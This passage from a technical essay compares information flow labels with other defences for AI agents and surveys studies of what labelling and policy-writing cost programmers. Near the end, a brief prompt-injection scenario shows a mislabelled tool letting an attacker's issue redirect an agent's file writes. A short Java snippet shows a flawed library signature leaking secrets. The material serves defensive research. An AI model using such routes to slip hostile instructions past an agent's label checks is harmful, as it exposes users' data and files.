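They were interested in defences that involve a person in some way, and sorted them into five kinds:

| Defence | How it works | Papers | Systems, of 21 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Scope settings | Someone limits the files, tools or networks the agent can reach | 4 | 16 |
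| Approvals | The agent pauses and a person allows or refuses an action | 5 | 15 |
| Written policies | Someone writes rules for what the agent may do | 13 | 14 |
| Trust labelling | Labels on data, tools or agents determine what may happen later | 8 | 0 |
| Intent anchoring | Software compares the agent's actions with the user's request or normal behaviour | 5 | 0 |

None of the 26 plugins used trust labels either. The eight papers on labelling include those on FIDES and CaMeL.

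Wang and colleagues' count of zero for labels covers only labels that users can see. They mention that Salesforce, which sells business software, has internal data labels in its Einstein Trust Layer, but they exclude these because users can't see them. That choice suits a study of how people and agents interact, but it makes the count a poor measure of how many products use labels at all. Jif programs, for example, have labels that the compiler uses and the people running the programs never see. Wang and colleagues also acknowledge that companies may have undocumented mechanisms.

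The count for written policies, by contrast, is too generous. The 14 production entries in the survey's detailed list are separate layers of policy that cover only 11 products, because Claude Code appears three times and Cursor, another coding agent, twice. According to the survey, five of the 14 layers also depend on the model obeying its instructions. For instance, Claude Code reads rules in ordinary English from a file called `CLAUDE.md` at the start of a session. A prompt injection can make the model ignore such rules, so they aren't a guardrail in the sense of a check outside the model. Comparing 14 with zero therefore holds policies to a looser standard than labels.

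The survey's classification of at least one labelling paper is also doubtful. The survey describes CaMeL as leaving a language model to propagate labels, but CaMeL is designed specifically to have an interpreter do this.

The main finding still holds. In May 2026 Microsoft, which had a product to promote, similarly said that most agents in production defended against prompt injection with either a warning in the system prompt or a homemade list of permitted actions. Agent makers had settled on approvals, scope limits and written rules, and rarely, if ever, used information flow labels.

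At least two of these companies knew the method well, so ignorance can't explain why they hadn't offered it to users by April 2026. Researchers at Google DeepMind and Microsoft published CaMeL and FIDES in 2025, and the 21 systems include Google's Gemini CLI and Microsoft Agent Framework. Wang and colleagues doubt that effort explains this kind of delay, since the versions that need the least labelling had no users either. They suspect that people don't naturally think of data as something that carries trust. But the papers had been out for only about a year, which is little time for a company to reject a method.

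### Labels in released products

Microsoft announced a version of FIDES on 20 May 2026, weeks after the survey's cut-off. It comes with Agent Framework, Microsoft's toolkit for building agents, from version 1.3.0. Microsoft marks it as experimental so that the company can keep changing how developers work with FIDES. After installing the toolkit, the checks stay off until a developer imports the security module and attaches it to an agent. Microsoft advises some developers to skip FIDES, including those whose agents have no powerful tools and those who are building a first prototype and would find labelling slow.

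Wang and colleagues might have had trouble classifying this product in their survey, because they could reasonably have counted it as an approval system, a labelling system or both. Developers write the labels, and users see them only when the software asks for approval, in a prompt that names the tool and the label that caused the block.

Microsoft also worked with GitHub, which it owns, on two related features. One is in the GitHub MCP server, which agents use to read and change projects on GitHub. If a developer adds a particular header to the configuration, the server labels the results of its tools, but it doesn't enforce anything. pkg.go.dev's *ifc* (2026), the documentation for GitHub's label code, states that the enforcement engine is a separate service. An agent that ignores the labels works as before and gets no protection from them.

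The other feature uses those labels. GitHub Copilot CLI, a terminal coding agent, keeps a context label and checks tool calls against it if the user starts the program with `FIDES_IFC=true`. Microsoft describes this support as experimental. It enforces policies only for selected tools from the GitHub server and does not yet support anyone else's MCP servers. Microsoft has also released a gateway that can add labels to results from other servers, and it plans to propose labels as an extension to MCP. For now, the labels work only between programs whose developers have agreed on a format.

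Even the GitHub labels seem unsettled. In Microsoft's account, issues from private projects are labelled as trusted. But in the code documentation, dated 18 May 2026, every issue is untrusted, even in private projects, because an attacker could control what it contains. The documented package is missing from the latest version of the server's code. GitHub may have moved it, because its notes on a later change still describe tool results with information flow labels attached.

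All three features began as options that a developer or user must switch on. The dated descriptions are from May 2026, so they don't show whether any of the three had become standard by the end of the year. Neither of Microsoft's posts gives usage figures. The Go documentation site lists no other public package that imports GitHub's label code, but that count wouldn't include people who run the server or connect an agent to it. Downloads of Agent Framework wouldn't show how many people use FIDES either, since most of the framework's users may never turn it on. Even those who do may be checking very little, because FIDES treats a tool's output as trusted and public if they forget to label the tool.

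## What labelling cost programmers

A programmer who adopts labels has to label the secrets, the code they pass through, and the libraries that code calls. Askarov and Sabelfeld described this work in unusual detail, because they wrote their poker program in ordinary Java before moving it to Jif. Later researchers counted labelled lines in other programs, and a few watched newcomers try to write labels or policies.

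### Moving a poker program from Java to Jif

The finished program has about 4,500 lines. Its two players, Alice and Bob, each have cards, encryption keys and a secret shuffle that the labels hide from the other player. Moving it to Jif involved seven kinds of work:

1. Write signatures for the Java library classes that the program uses. A signature lists a class's methods with labels added, so that the compiler can check calls to code that has none.
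2. Replace some library classes with versions written in Jif, such as Jif's own `ArrayList` in place of Java's `Vector`.
3. Turn labels into parameters of a class. Otherwise the program would need one `Player` class for Alice and another for Bob, identical except for their labels.
4. Label the fields of each class.
5. Label the methods and their arguments. A method can also have a begin-label, which limits where in a program other code may call it, and an end-label, which covers what the caller learns from whether it finishes normally.
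6. Deal with every error that could occur while the program runs. A Java programmer can ignore the chance of dividing by zero. In Jif that isn't allowed, because an error from dividing by a secret number reveals that the number is zero.
7. Write helper code to relabel large data structures. If a program could relabel an array in one step, it might end up with a secret name and a public name for the same array, then write a secret through one and read it through the other. It has to copy the array element by element instead.

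Askarov and Sabelfeld went around these steps many times. A label on one variable forced labels onto the methods that used it, and they then rewrote those methods to remove the flow or declare it openly. Even a short method heading fills up quickly. Here is one of their examples, below its plain Java equivalent:

```
boolean validate(String s, int hash)

boolean{Alice:Bob} validate{Alice:}(String{} s, int{} hash):{Alice:}
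```

The Jif heading has five labels. The label on the result lets Alice and Bob read it, the empty braces make both arguments public, and the two copies of `{Alice:}` are the begin-label and the end-label.

Askarov, then a graduate student, did all the coding. He spent about 60 hours on the Java version and another 150 on the Jif version, not counting the time to learn Jif, so adding labels to a working program took two and a half times as long as writing it. A version in which the players run as separate processes took a further 80 hours. The ratio comes from one person and one program. A second program might have gone faster, because Askarov and Sabelfeld worked out reusable coding patterns along the way, but other Java programmers might take longer, since few have an information flow specialist as a co-author.

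The programmers spent some of the hours working around gaps in the tools. Jif had no debugger, so they debugged the Java version. It also couldn't convert labelled objects into text to send between players, so they wrote the conversion code by hand for every class.

In return, the labels exposed some weaknesses in the Java version. If an error occurred while the program was handling secret data, the error and its details could reach public code. Askarov and Sabelfeld hadn't noticed these leaks before, though they saw no obvious way to exploit them. They thought the labelled program was still fairly close to the original.

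### Labels for code that someone else wrote

The whole guarantee depends on the library signatures. The compiler checks each call against the signature and never examines the library's own code, so if the signature is wrong, the compiler will accept code that leaks.

This had already happened in the signatures that came with Jif. Java programs use `System.arraycopy` to copy one array into another, and Askarov and Sabelfeld showed that it could copy secrets into a public array:

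```
private int{L}[] secret;
private int{}[]  output;

System.arraycopy(secret, 0, output, 0, secret.length);
```

The compiler accepted this signature even though it had no begin-label. In Jif, omitting the begin-label means that a method has no side effects, but this method writes into an array. The signature also described both arrays as objects, which left no place to state the labels on their elements. If a mistake like this could get into Jif's own distribution, an application programmer working through an unfamiliar library would probably make some too.

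Programmers may have to write many signatures. Chong and colleagues needed 960 lines of them for their web programs, on top of about 4,040 lines of Java for the framework itself. Ernst, Just and colleagues annotated 10,470 library methods by hand for the Android label checker they describe in *Collaborative Verification of Information Flow for a High-Assurance App Store* (2014). Later users can share this work, so the effort per program falls as a tool becomes popular. But a new tool has few users to share it, and anyone whose program needs a library that nobody has labelled must label it first.

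Filament, the 2026 Rust library, mostly avoids signatures. When a program passes labelled data to an ordinary library function, Filament gives the result the join of the arguments' labels. The programmer only has to wrap the call, but Ching and colleagues have to assume that the function doesn't send the data somewhere itself.

Agent developers face a version of the signature problem with tools. The software around an agent can't inspect the internals of a tool that someone else runs, so it relies on whatever label the tool's developer or a wrapper supplies. An agent may need only a dozen of these labels instead of thousands, but writing them still seems to take judgement, since accounts conflict on how GitHub labels issues in private projects.

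### A quarter of the lines in two web programs

Chong and colleagues counted the labelled lines in their web email program, their shared calendar and the code for user accounts that both programs use:

| Code | Lines | Lines with labels | Share |
|---|---|---|---|
| Web email | 1,325 | 277 | 21% |
| Shared calendar | 1,779 | 443 | 25% |
| User accounts | 925 | 283 | 31% |
| Total | 4,029 | 1,003 | 25% |

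About a quarter of the lines had labels, even though the compiler inferred many other labels. This fraction understates how much programmers had to write, since one line can hold five labels, as in `validate`.

The counts come from the finished programs, so they leave out revisions. Chong and colleagues sometimes changed a method's labels several times. They found flows they had missed in the design when they wrote the method's body, and found more when they called the method from a new place. They had built this version of Jif themselves, so unfamiliarity with the language doesn't explain the rework.

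Some flows are hard to see in code that looks harmless. They give this example as a common trap for new Jif programmers:

```
x = o.m();
y = 42;
```

If the object `o` doesn't exist, the first line causes an error and the second never runs. Anyone who can see whether `y` became 42 therefore learns whether `o` exists, even though the second line only assigns a constant. The programmer can remove the flow by first testing whether `o` exists and calling the method only if it does. Java programmers know that such a call can fail, but they have no reason to think of it as a branch that leaks information.

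### The app-store experiment

Ernst and colleagues wanted to split the work between the developer who writes an app and an auditor at the store that distributes it. The developer submits source code with labels and a flow policy, a short list of where each kind of data may go. An audio recorder, for example, needs a line that lets sound from the microphone reach the file system. A line that let it reach the internet would look suspicious. The labels in the code name the same sources and destinations:

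```
@Source(LOCATION) @Sink(INTERNET) double loc;
```

A label might mark a number as one that may come from the phone's location and may go to the internet. The app store's checker verifies that the labels match the code and the policy, and the auditor decides whether the policy makes sense for the app.

To measure the developer's share of the work, five members of the research team labelled 11 apps they had never seen before, totalling 9,437 lines. For each app, they started with unlabelled code and a flow policy, and added labels until the checker gave no more warnings. They wrote 580 annotations in about 26 hours, or about 6 per 100 lines of code. They spent most of that time understanding the code, so the original developers would probably have been faster.

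Two graduate students then audited the apps. They hadn't used the checker before and didn't know which apps were malicious. For each app, they wrote a flow policy from the app's description and compared it with the one submitted. They also read the developer's reasons for any exceptions and looked for indirect leaks. The audit took 269 minutes, or roughly 30 minutes per 1,000 lines. They rejected the one malicious app and accepted the other ten.

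Ernst and colleagues put their annotation burden at less than a quarter of Jif's. The raw numbers are consistent with this, but programmers do different work in the two systems. Jif's compiler tracks implicit flows with the pc label, and the programmer has to satisfy the compiler's checks. The Android checker only flags each condition that depends on sensitive data, and an auditor reads the code that follows. The auditors reviewed 213 conditions in the 11 apps, so they did some of the work that Jif leaves to programmers. The Android labels also come from a ready-made list of phone resources, while users of the Jif calendar can set their own policies while the program is running.

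The largest app had only 1,547 lines. At the same rate, auditing an app of 100,000 lines would take about 50 hours. Ernst and colleagues expected updates to take much less work to check, but they didn't measure this.

The researchers did have a comparison group for a related task, finding malware. DARPA, which funded the project, hired five companies to write 72 apps, 57 of them malicious. It also hired a separate team of four PhD students to look for malware in two batches of the apps with other tools. The students had about as much Java and Android experience as the researchers.

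| Batch | Team | Time per app | Correct verdicts |
|---|---|---|---|
| Third | PhD students, other tools | 9.5 hours | 60% |
| Third | Researchers, label checker | 42 minutes | 80% |
| Fifth | PhD students, other tools | 2.3 hours | 63% |
| Fifth | Researchers, label checker | 1.25 hours | 75% |

The label checker's users were faster and more accurate both times, but they had built the checker themselves. Their lead in speed shrank from about fourteenfold to less than twofold. The results suggest that labels help someone who has to judge unfamiliar code, but there is little evidence that they help a developer who trusts their own code and has to write the labels. Ernst and colleagues raise the possibility that stores would pay developers extra to write them.

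### Cost follows the protected data

Filament's figures vary much more than the earlier ones. Ching and colleagues added labels to five existing programs, including their Rust translation of the email client that Hicks and colleagues wrote in Jif in 2006.

| Program | What the labels protect | Original lines | Lines with labels | Labels as a share of original lines |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Calendar | Two people's free days | 29 | 14 | 48% |
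| Battleship | Positions of the ships | 286 | 16 | 6% |
| Spotify client | Login details | 10,912 | 36 | 0.3% |
| Servo, a browser engine | Responses from other websites | 327,096 | 61 | 0.02% |
| Email client | Passwords, messages and private keys | 1,894 | 199 | 11% |

Servo is more than 170 times as long as the email client but needed less than a third as many labelled lines. The only rule in its policy is that a script from one website may not read responses from another. Only a small part of the browser engine handles those responses, whereas almost all of the email client handles protected text.

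The work of labelling a program therefore depends more on how much of its code touches protected data than on its size. Ernst and colleagues found the same pattern on a smaller scale, where a 520-line calculator needed 7 annotations and a 625-line app called Dynalogin needed 66. The pattern doesn't depend on Filament's design either. Ching and colleagues counted 64 labelled lines that Cocoon, an earlier Rust tool, needed to enforce the same rule in Servo.

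The researchers chose to protect only one thing in the browser, which let them keep the count low, at 61 lines. Securing the whole browser would take more labels, because it also holds passwords, cookies and browsing history, and each would need its own policy. Filament's labels are also simpler than those in the Jif web programs, because the programmer has to set them all before the program runs.

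These figures are still encouraging for large programs whose secrets stay in one small part of the code. They are less encouraging for programs like email clients, where a leak would matter most and labelling takes the most work. An agent that reads a user's mailbox and files handles protected data at nearly every step, so it resembles the email client more than Servo. But its developers mostly label tools and data sources, so the number of labelled lines is a poor measure of their workload.

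### What newcomers managed

Most of these numbers come from specialists. To see how beginners would do, Ernst and colleagues gave their checker to 32 third-year undergraduates in a compilers class, 60 per cent of whom had never used Android. The students heard a two-hour presentation and then worked in pairs to label an Android app of 1,000 to 1,500 lines.

The task took the students 15 hours on average, when it would have taken three or four at the research team's pace. But the students were learning Android, information flow and the checker at once, and said the work became easier after the first few annotations. Ernst and colleagues call the study "extremely preliminary", but it suggests that a student can learn to satisfy the checker within a couple of working days. It doesn't show whether students would choose to do so on their own projects.

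Giffin, Heule and colleagues write in *Security and the Average Programmer* that limited adoption by non-experts has historically been a weakness of this kind of system. They hoped to do better with Hails, their framework for building websites in Haskell. A Hails program keeps its policies in separate code that labels the contents of the database, so whoever writes the rest of the site can largely leave security to that code. In the five deployed programs with their own policy code, it made up 9% to 18% of the lines, excluding libraries.

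The Hails team collected reports from seven developers and interviewed four of them. None had built a website in Haskell before. They understood the division between policy code and the rest, and they liked not having to scatter security checks through their programs. But most of them struggled to write policies in the early version, in which a policy was ordinary program code, so the team designed a small language for policies. Developers then wrote correct policies in less time.

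In the new language, marking a database field as a `key` made it searchable but also exposed it to any code that could search that part of the database. One developer wanted visitors to be able to search a blog, so they marked the text of the articles as a key, even though they had written a fairly strict policy for the articles. Other developers made similar mistakes. After watching people outside the team use the language, the team renamed the marker `public-index`, which makes the exposure much harder to miss.

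### What a designer's own case study leaves out

A designer who builds a program in their own language shows that it can be done. The hours and line counts are probably closer to the minimum than to what a typical programmer would need, because the designer knows what the compiler will accept and can fix the language when it causes problems. The designer also picks the program, and researchers rarely publish accounts of programs they gave up on. We can't tell from such examples how many ordinary programmers would finish the same job or think it worth starting.

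A better test would randomly assign programmers to write the same program with or without labels, then compare the time they took and the leaks that remained. None of the studies described here did that, and such experiments seem to be rare. *120 Domain-Specific Languages for Security* (2024), a review of specialised languages for security work, concludes that researchers need to improve the languages' usability and evaluation. Researchers have run this sort of experiment on cryptographic libraries with 256 Python programmers, so it is feasible. Many of those programmers believed their code was secure when it wasn't, which line counts would not have revealed.

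### Two studies of people writing policies

The next best evidence comes from related tools. Wang, Görz and colleagues (2025), in *Anota*, asked 11 people to annotate six Python programs. The participants had used neither the tool nor the programs before. Anota checks the annotations as a program runs, while another tool bombards the program with unusual inputs. Some annotations restrict which files a program may open or which code it may run. Others are a form of taint tracking and come closer to labels:

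```
TAINT(pwd, sanitization=[hash], Sink=[print])
```

This follows a password through the program and reports a violation if the program prints it without hashing it first.

Each program contained a known flaw, and the participants' annotations caught it in 55 of 66 attempts. The reported average time ranged from 40 to 86 minutes per program. Seven of the 11 failures involved one program, where the annotator had to know which users should have access to a particular feature. Ten of the 11 participants succeeded on the program whose flaw leaked sensitive information, typically in about an hour.

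The number of annotations varied widely between participants. For one program, a participant caught the flaw with 3 annotations and no false alarms, while another wrote 127 and had 18 false alarms. Participants generally preferred forbidding specific bad behaviour to listing everything a program was allowed to do. Forbidding is quicker, but it only protects against dangers the writer thought of.

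Wang, Görz and colleagues also interviewed ten professional developers and security analysts. All ten agreed that finding this kind of flaw in an important program was worth an hour of annotation, and all named having to learn a new annotation language as a barrier. Their answers may overstate their willingness to annotate, because telling the tool's designers that the work is worthwhile takes much less effort than doing it.

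In *Playing in the Sandbox*, Alhindi and Hallett (2025) studied Seccomp, a tool they hadn't designed. It is a Linux feature that lets a program limit which requests it can make to the operating system, such as opening a file or connecting to a network. The researchers recruited seven developers who had used Seccomp before, paid them about $250 each, and gave them an hour to restrict a 115-line program that checked whether a remote server was reachable and logged the result.

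Six of the seven developers produced a working restriction, and no two were the same. All six listed what the program could do and blocked everything else, the opposite of what the Anota participants preferred. They all said they wanted to allow only what the program needed, but their lists ranged from 9 kinds of request to 27. Two left out the request the program uses to shut down after an error. One of those two had copied the list from a recording of the program's requests, so it also allowed everything the program did while starting up. Another developer's list was too broad in the same way. Only one developer restricted the details of a request as well as its type.

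Alhindi and Hallett call their sample "tiny" and don't generalise from it. But the participants were experienced, and the program was very short and had no hidden behaviour. If they disagreed this much about what it needed, developers writing policies for larger programs will probably disagree more.

Seccomp isn't widely used either. Alhindi and Hallett cite an earlier count which found that only 802 of the tens of thousands of software packages for Debian and Fedora, two popular versions of Linux, used sandboxing directly in their code. So a general reluctance to write security policies, as well as the particular burden of labels, may help explain why few programmers use security-typed languages.

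Studies of people writing policies for agents also seem scarce, so seccomp is one of the closer comparisons. A developer who decides which tools an agent may use has to make the same kind of list. But the actions an agent needs can change with every user request, while the watchdog program in the seccomp study did the same thing every few seconds.

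## Inferring labels instead of writing them

Most of the labels in a program follow from a few others. If `salary` is secret and a program computes `bonus` from it, `bonus` has to be secret too. A compiler can fill in such labels by treating the program as a set of constraints and solving them.

### Solving for the missing labels

This small program belongs to a staff directory, which shows a badge next to each current employee:

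```
secret int  salary     // from the payroll file
public bool badge      // visible to anyone

1   bonus  = salary / 10
2   large  = false
3   if bonus > 5000:  large = true
4   active = true
5   badge  = active
```

The code has five variables but only two written labels. The compiler gives each of the other three an unknown label: B for `bonus`, L for `large` and A for `active`. It then applies the assignment rule, label(e) ⊔ pc ⊑ label(x), to each line.

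| Line | Constraint | Reason |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | secret ⊑ B | `bonus` depends on `salary` |
| 2 | public ⊑ L | a constant is public |
| 3 | B ⊑ L | pc is B inside the branch |
| 4 | public ⊑ A | a constant is public |
| 5 | A ⊑ public | `badge` is public |

The solver starts with every unknown label at public and raises one only when a constraint requires it. It raises B to secret because of line 1, then L to secret because of line 3. A stays public. All five constraints now hold, so the program passes. The programmer wrote only two of the five labels, and the solver inferred the other three.

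The solver raises a label only when a constraint requires it, so it ends with the least restrictive labels possible. If those labels still violate a constraint, no other labels would work. Suppose someone changes line 5 to `badge = large`, so that the directory shows a badge only for people with large bonuses. The last constraint becomes L ⊑ public, but the earlier constraints already forced L to be secret, which proves that the code conflicts with the two written labels.

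It hasn't found the mistake, though. Lines 1, 3 and 5 form a chain,

secret ⊑ B ⊑ L ⊑ public,

and breaking any link would remove the conflict. Perhaps line 5 should have used `active`, or line 3 should have tested something other than the bonus. If only payroll staff can see the directory, the code is fine and the label on `badge` is wrong. The constraints are the same in every case.

Jif's solver raises the lowest label a variable could have, lowers the highest, and reports an error where the two cross. *SHErrLoc* (Zhang, Myers and colleagues, 2017) gives an example based on a Jif programmer's code. The compiler reports an error on line 3, but the mistake is on line 1, where the programmer wrote the empty label `{}`, which means public.

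### How far inference reaches

Jif infers labels within one method at a time. It works out the labels of local variables, such as `match` in the password class, but checks each call against the called method's heading. Programmers therefore have to label fields and method headings themselves, unless Jif's defaults are suitable. This helps explain why a quarter of the lines in the Jif web programs had labels despite the inference.

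Flow Caml infers labels for whole functions. For a function that adds 1 to a number, it infers that the result has the same label as the argument, so the same function works on both secret and public numbers.

JLift, which King and colleagues used for their 2008 study, extends Jif's inference to whole programs written in ordinary Java. The programmer labels only the secrets and the public outputs. JLift summarizes each method as a set of constraints that connect its arguments to its results, and applies that summary wherever the program calls the method.

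JLift keeps a separate copy of a method's constraints for every call. Otherwise, a single call with a secret argument would make the method's results secret everywhere. For libraries, JLift gives each object one label that covers everything going in or out, instead of analyzing the library code. A secret stored in a list is therefore still labeled secret when the program takes it out.

Filament gets its inference from Rust. Ching and colleagues made the label part of a value's type, and Rust's compiler already works out most of the types inside a function. If `x` has label A, the programmer can write

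```
let z = fcall!(foo(x, relabel!(y, A)));
```

without giving `z` a label. But Rust's inference looks for types that match, and it has no built-in notion that public data may become secret. The programmer has to raise the public value `y` by hand, using `relabel!`. An ordinary function such as `foo` needs no labels in its heading, because `fcall!` adds them for the call. A function that works on labelled values directly does need them there, since Rust doesn't infer the types in headings.

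Wider inference saves writing but makes the chains longer. A label on a method heading is tedious to write, but it stops a conflict from spreading beyond that method. Without it, the compiler may report an error in a file that the programmer has never opened. Zhang and colleagues see this as a general trade-off, because inference saves work by drawing on distant parts of a program, which also makes it hard to tell which part is at fault.

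### Finding the line that is wrong

One remedy is to show the programmer the whole chain that led to a conflict. In *Effective Blame for Information-Flow Violations*, King, Jaeger and colleagues (2008) changed the solver to record how labels depend on one another. When a conflict occurs, their tool uses those records to report everything that contributed to it and nothing else. For the leaking directory program, such a report would list lines 1, 3 and 5. They found that programmers could generally explain and fix an error by looking at a small fraction of the code, although the programmer still has to decide which link in the chain is wrong.

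SHErrLoc also guesses which code is wrong. Its ranking is based on the assumption that most of the code is correct, so it favors explanations with few mistakes and treats code as less likely to be wrong if it also appears in chains that hold. If the directory program had a sixth line that copied `bonus` to a secret payslip, the chain secret ⊑ B ⊑ secret would hold, and it would include line 1. Lines 3 and 5 would appear only in the chain that fails, so they would be more likely to be wrong than line 1.

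The tool can also suggest that the code is right but an assumption is missing. For example, data may move from a patient's label to a doctor's only if the program declares that the doctor can act for the patient.

Zhang and colleagues tested SHErrLoc on 16 errors that a developer had recorded while working on FriendMap, an application written in Fabric, an extension of Jif. Two people took six weeks to write FriendMap. Eleven of the errors were missing assumptions, and the other five were wrong expressions.

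| How SHErrLoc presented its suggestions | Errors located |
|---|---|
| One ranked list of both kinds | 11 of 16 |
| A separate list for each kind | 14 of 16 |
| The programmer confirms missing assumptions first | 15 of 16 |

The tool's higher score of 96% comes from ordinary type errors in 336 student OCaml programs, which had no security labels. The FriendMap sample is small and comes from one application, but the errors are real. The best result also required a programmer to answer questions about who trusts whom.

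In another test, Zhang and colleagues randomly deleted assumptions from Jif and Fabric code to make 40 files, each missing one to five. SHErrLoc suggested the deleted assumptions for 17 files and found weaker ones that sufficed for another 11. The remaining 12 files passed the check anyway, so their programmers had declared trust that the code didn't need.

### What the solver cannot work out

Inference spreads labels through a program, but a person must still decide what is secret and who may see it. SHErrLoc may suggest that a doctor can act for a patient because this would remove an error, but whether the doctor should have that power depends on the hospital. Similarly, if the programmer forgets to write `secret` on the first line of the directory program, the solver leaves every label at public, and even the leaking version passes.

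The person may also have to decide when the policy changes. In *Sound Enforcement of Dynamic Release Information Flow Policy*, Ching and Zhang (2026) argue that fixed policies are part of the reason few real systems use information flow analysis. Their extension to Rust lets a programmer label a card number so that a merchant may use it until a transaction ends, and nobody may use it afterwards. The programmer writes this condition into the label and marks the point where the transaction ends. A solver couldn't infer from unlabelled code that the merchant must then stop using the number.

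### Labels for an agent's tools

An agent's software automatically gives the model's own text the context label, so nobody has to label each message, though someone still has to describe the tools by hand. *Optimizing Agent Planning for Security and Autonomy* (2026) describes this default as conservative, since the model may have used only part of what it read.

Microsoft's gateway, which adds labels to results from MCP servers that don't supply any, needs three things for each tool:

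- **An output schema**, which lists the fields in the tool's results so that labels can apply to them separately.
- **A propagation function**, written in Python, which works out the labels on the results from the labels on the arguments.
- **A policy**, which decides whether to allow a call, block it or ask a person. Developers can write one in Rego, a language for such rules, or choose a built-in one.

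Microsoft's label format saves some of this work. A label on one part of a result covers everything nested inside it and passes up to any container without a label of its own. But a policy can take some thought to write, such as the one for posting in a chat channel, which has to call another tool to find out who belongs to the channel. So far Microsoft has set up the gateway for selected tools in its own Work IQ servers, which connect agents to services such as email and Teams.

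A cheaper route uses annotations that a tool's developer may already have supplied. MCP has yes-or-no hints for whether a tool only reads data, whether it deals with an "open world" of outside parties (as a web search does), and whether it may destroy something. Microsoft suggests turning them into policies like this:

| Annotations | Policy |
|---|---|
| Read-only, not open-world | Always allow |
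| Read-only, open-world | Allow only if every argument is public |
| Destructive | Ask the user |

The second policy is needed because a search query can leak a secret even if the search changes nothing. To label a tool's results, the software can assume that every argument may flow into them, then add "untrusted" if the tool is open-world and "private" if it requires authentication.

These labels are safe only if the annotations are accurate. *Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* (2026) objects that MCP makes annotations optional and advises treating tools as untrusted, so an agent can't count on reliable labels. Under the first policy, a tool falsely annotated as read-only and closed could collect private data on every call.

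Honest developers could make mistakes as well. Someone might mark a mailbox tool as closed because it reads only the user's own mailbox. Its results would then not be labeled "untrusted", even though strangers write much of the mail. The derived labels are also coarse. They could mark all of Alex's email as private, but they wouldn't record that Priya may read one message and Marco another.

*Towards Verifiably Safe Tool Use for LLM Agents* proposes making labels compulsory but allowing "unsure" as a label, which makes the agent ask for confirmation. *APPA* (2026) instead lets developers add labels gradually and supports tools that have none.

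### Labels and policies written by language models

Since tools come with written descriptions, a language model can draft the labels. *AgentArmor* (2025) generates them from descriptions of a tool's parameters and return values. *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* (2026) compared how OpenAI's o1 and human annotators labeled 80 tools on five attributes, including how much harm a tool could do and whether its results might contain an attack.

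The researchers measured agreement with Cohen's kappa, which is 1 for perfect agreement and 0 for chance agreement. Kappa was 0.95 overall but only 0.77 for sensitivity, the attribute that covers potential harm. For instance, the human annotators rated a tool that opens web pages as moderately sensitive because it could help a phishing attack, while o1 rated its sensitivity as low. The researchers concluded that people should review the model's labels but needn't write them from scratch.

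In *CTO*, Mayoral-Vilches (2026) tested models on 116 constructed tool calls with four labels each. The largest, with 800 billion parameters, got 88.1% of the labels right, barely more than the 87.9% from one with 30 billion. If the largest model's mistakes were spread at random, it would get all four labels right on about 60% of calls. The true share is probably higher, because mistakes tend to cluster on hard cases.

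Whole policies seem to be harder. *Structured Decomposition for Reliable LLM-Generated Access Control Policies* (2026) tested a model on translating 372 access-control requirements for general software into Rego. With a direct prompt, the model wrote a fully correct policy for fewer than one in six, mostly because it rejected valid requirements and produced nothing, which a developer would at least notice.

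Both the directly prompted model and a more structured pipeline wrote policies for 77 of the requirements. The directly prompted policies all compiled, but some had less visible failures. Of the eight checked for complete rules denying access, only three had them, compared with seven from the pipeline.

*Environment Steering* (2026) has a model write data-flow policies for each task an agent receives. When the user asks for a summary of one patient's visit, for example, the model writes a rule against mentioning other patients. The researchers checked the policies by hand and still warned that some might be missing or too permissive.

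In *AgentSpec*, Wang, Poskitt and Sun (2025) had o1 write rules to stop risky actions by three kinds of agent. These rules restrict actions and don't label data, but having o1 write them is a similar test of whether a model can write a guardrail.

| Agent | Rules written | Risky cases tested | Cases stopped |
|---|---|---|---|
| Coding agent | 25 | 675 | 87.26% |
| Household robot | 10 | 225 | 95.56% |
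| Self-driving car | 6 | 8 | 62.5% |

In this work's robot test, the generated rules stopped 215 of the 225 risky tasks and missed ten. Wang, Li and Tian, in their survey of agent products, cite the test's reported recall of 70.96% as meaning that the rules miss nearly 30% of the necessary constraints. The experiment doesn't support that reading, because it counted risky cases rather than constraints.

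The AgentSpec paper calls the 95.56% "precision", although the share of dangerous cases caught is normally called recall. It calculates the 70.96% partly from harmless versions of the tasks, so that figure may be the share of harmless tasks that the rules allowed. But the paper explains it as dangerous tasks that the rules missed, which is hard to reconcile with the 95.56%. The 70.96% is therefore poor evidence of how much a model leaves out.

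The individual failures are more informative. A coding rule meant to protect configuration files covered only the ones named in the examples. A robot rule about heating didn't classify putting a kettle full of wine on the stove as unsafe. Another rule banned all pouring, so the robot couldn't water a houseplant. Current models would probably avoid some of these mistakes, since o1 dates from 2024.

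### What one wrong label does to the guarantee

Noninterference protects only data that is labeled correctly. If someone labels a secret as public, the proof still holds but doesn't cover that secret. *ToolGuardian* (2026), which checks tool calls with fixed logical rules, likewise notes that its results are deterministic but can be wrong if a rule or a fact about a tool is missing.

Suppose a model labelled `read_issue` as trusted for the agent that sorts bug reports. The context would stay trusted after the agent read the attacker's issue, and a call to `write_file` would pass. Every attack by this route would get through until someone corrected the label, whereas a filter that misses 5% of attacks still stops most of them. The wrong label wouldn't affect the check on `post_comment`, which depends on the confidentiality label, so that call would still fail once the agent had read `.env`.

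A label that is too strict can block useful work, but it doesn't leak anything. A model could therefore get 12% of labels wrong and still preserve the guarantee if every mistake was too strict. One label that is too lax could break the guarantee, even if the model is 99% accurate. The kappa scores and Mayoral-Vilches's percentages don't distinguish between the two kinds of mistake.

Developers can tell a model to choose the stricter label when in doubt. *Taming Various Privilege Escalation in LLM-Based Agent Systems* does this with a tool-labelling prompt that urges caution before marking anything as trusted. In one test, the system treated Wikipedia text as possibly malicious, then wrongly flagged two legitimate tasks as attacks when the agent tried to record health data or register an appointment. The paper suggests labelling Wikipedia as trusted in a real deployment, even though anyone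 can edit it.

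## False alarms and labels that only become stricter

Even when every label is correct, the check can reject code that leaks nothing. In their 2008 study, King and colleagues measured how often this happens by running JLift, their checker for ordinary Java, on six security functions from two libraries. Three functions, from the J2SSH library, log users in to a server over SSH, a standard for secure remote access. The other three, from the cryptography library Bouncy Castle, encrypt or hash data. The secrets included passwords and keys. The researchers checked the alarms by hand and counted one as real only if they could confirm that the program could take the path it flagged.

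| Function | Library | Alarms | False alarms | Share false |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Password login | J2SSH | 7 | 3 | 43% |
| Keyboard-interactive login | J2SSH | 23 | 19 | 83% |
| Public-key login | J2SSH | 170 | 111 | 65% |
| RSA encryption | Bouncy Castle | 218 | 186 | 85% |
| MD5 hashing | Bouncy Castle | 209 | 199 | 95% |
| DES encryption | Bouncy Castle | 260 | 207 | 80% |
| Total | | 887 | 725 | 82% |

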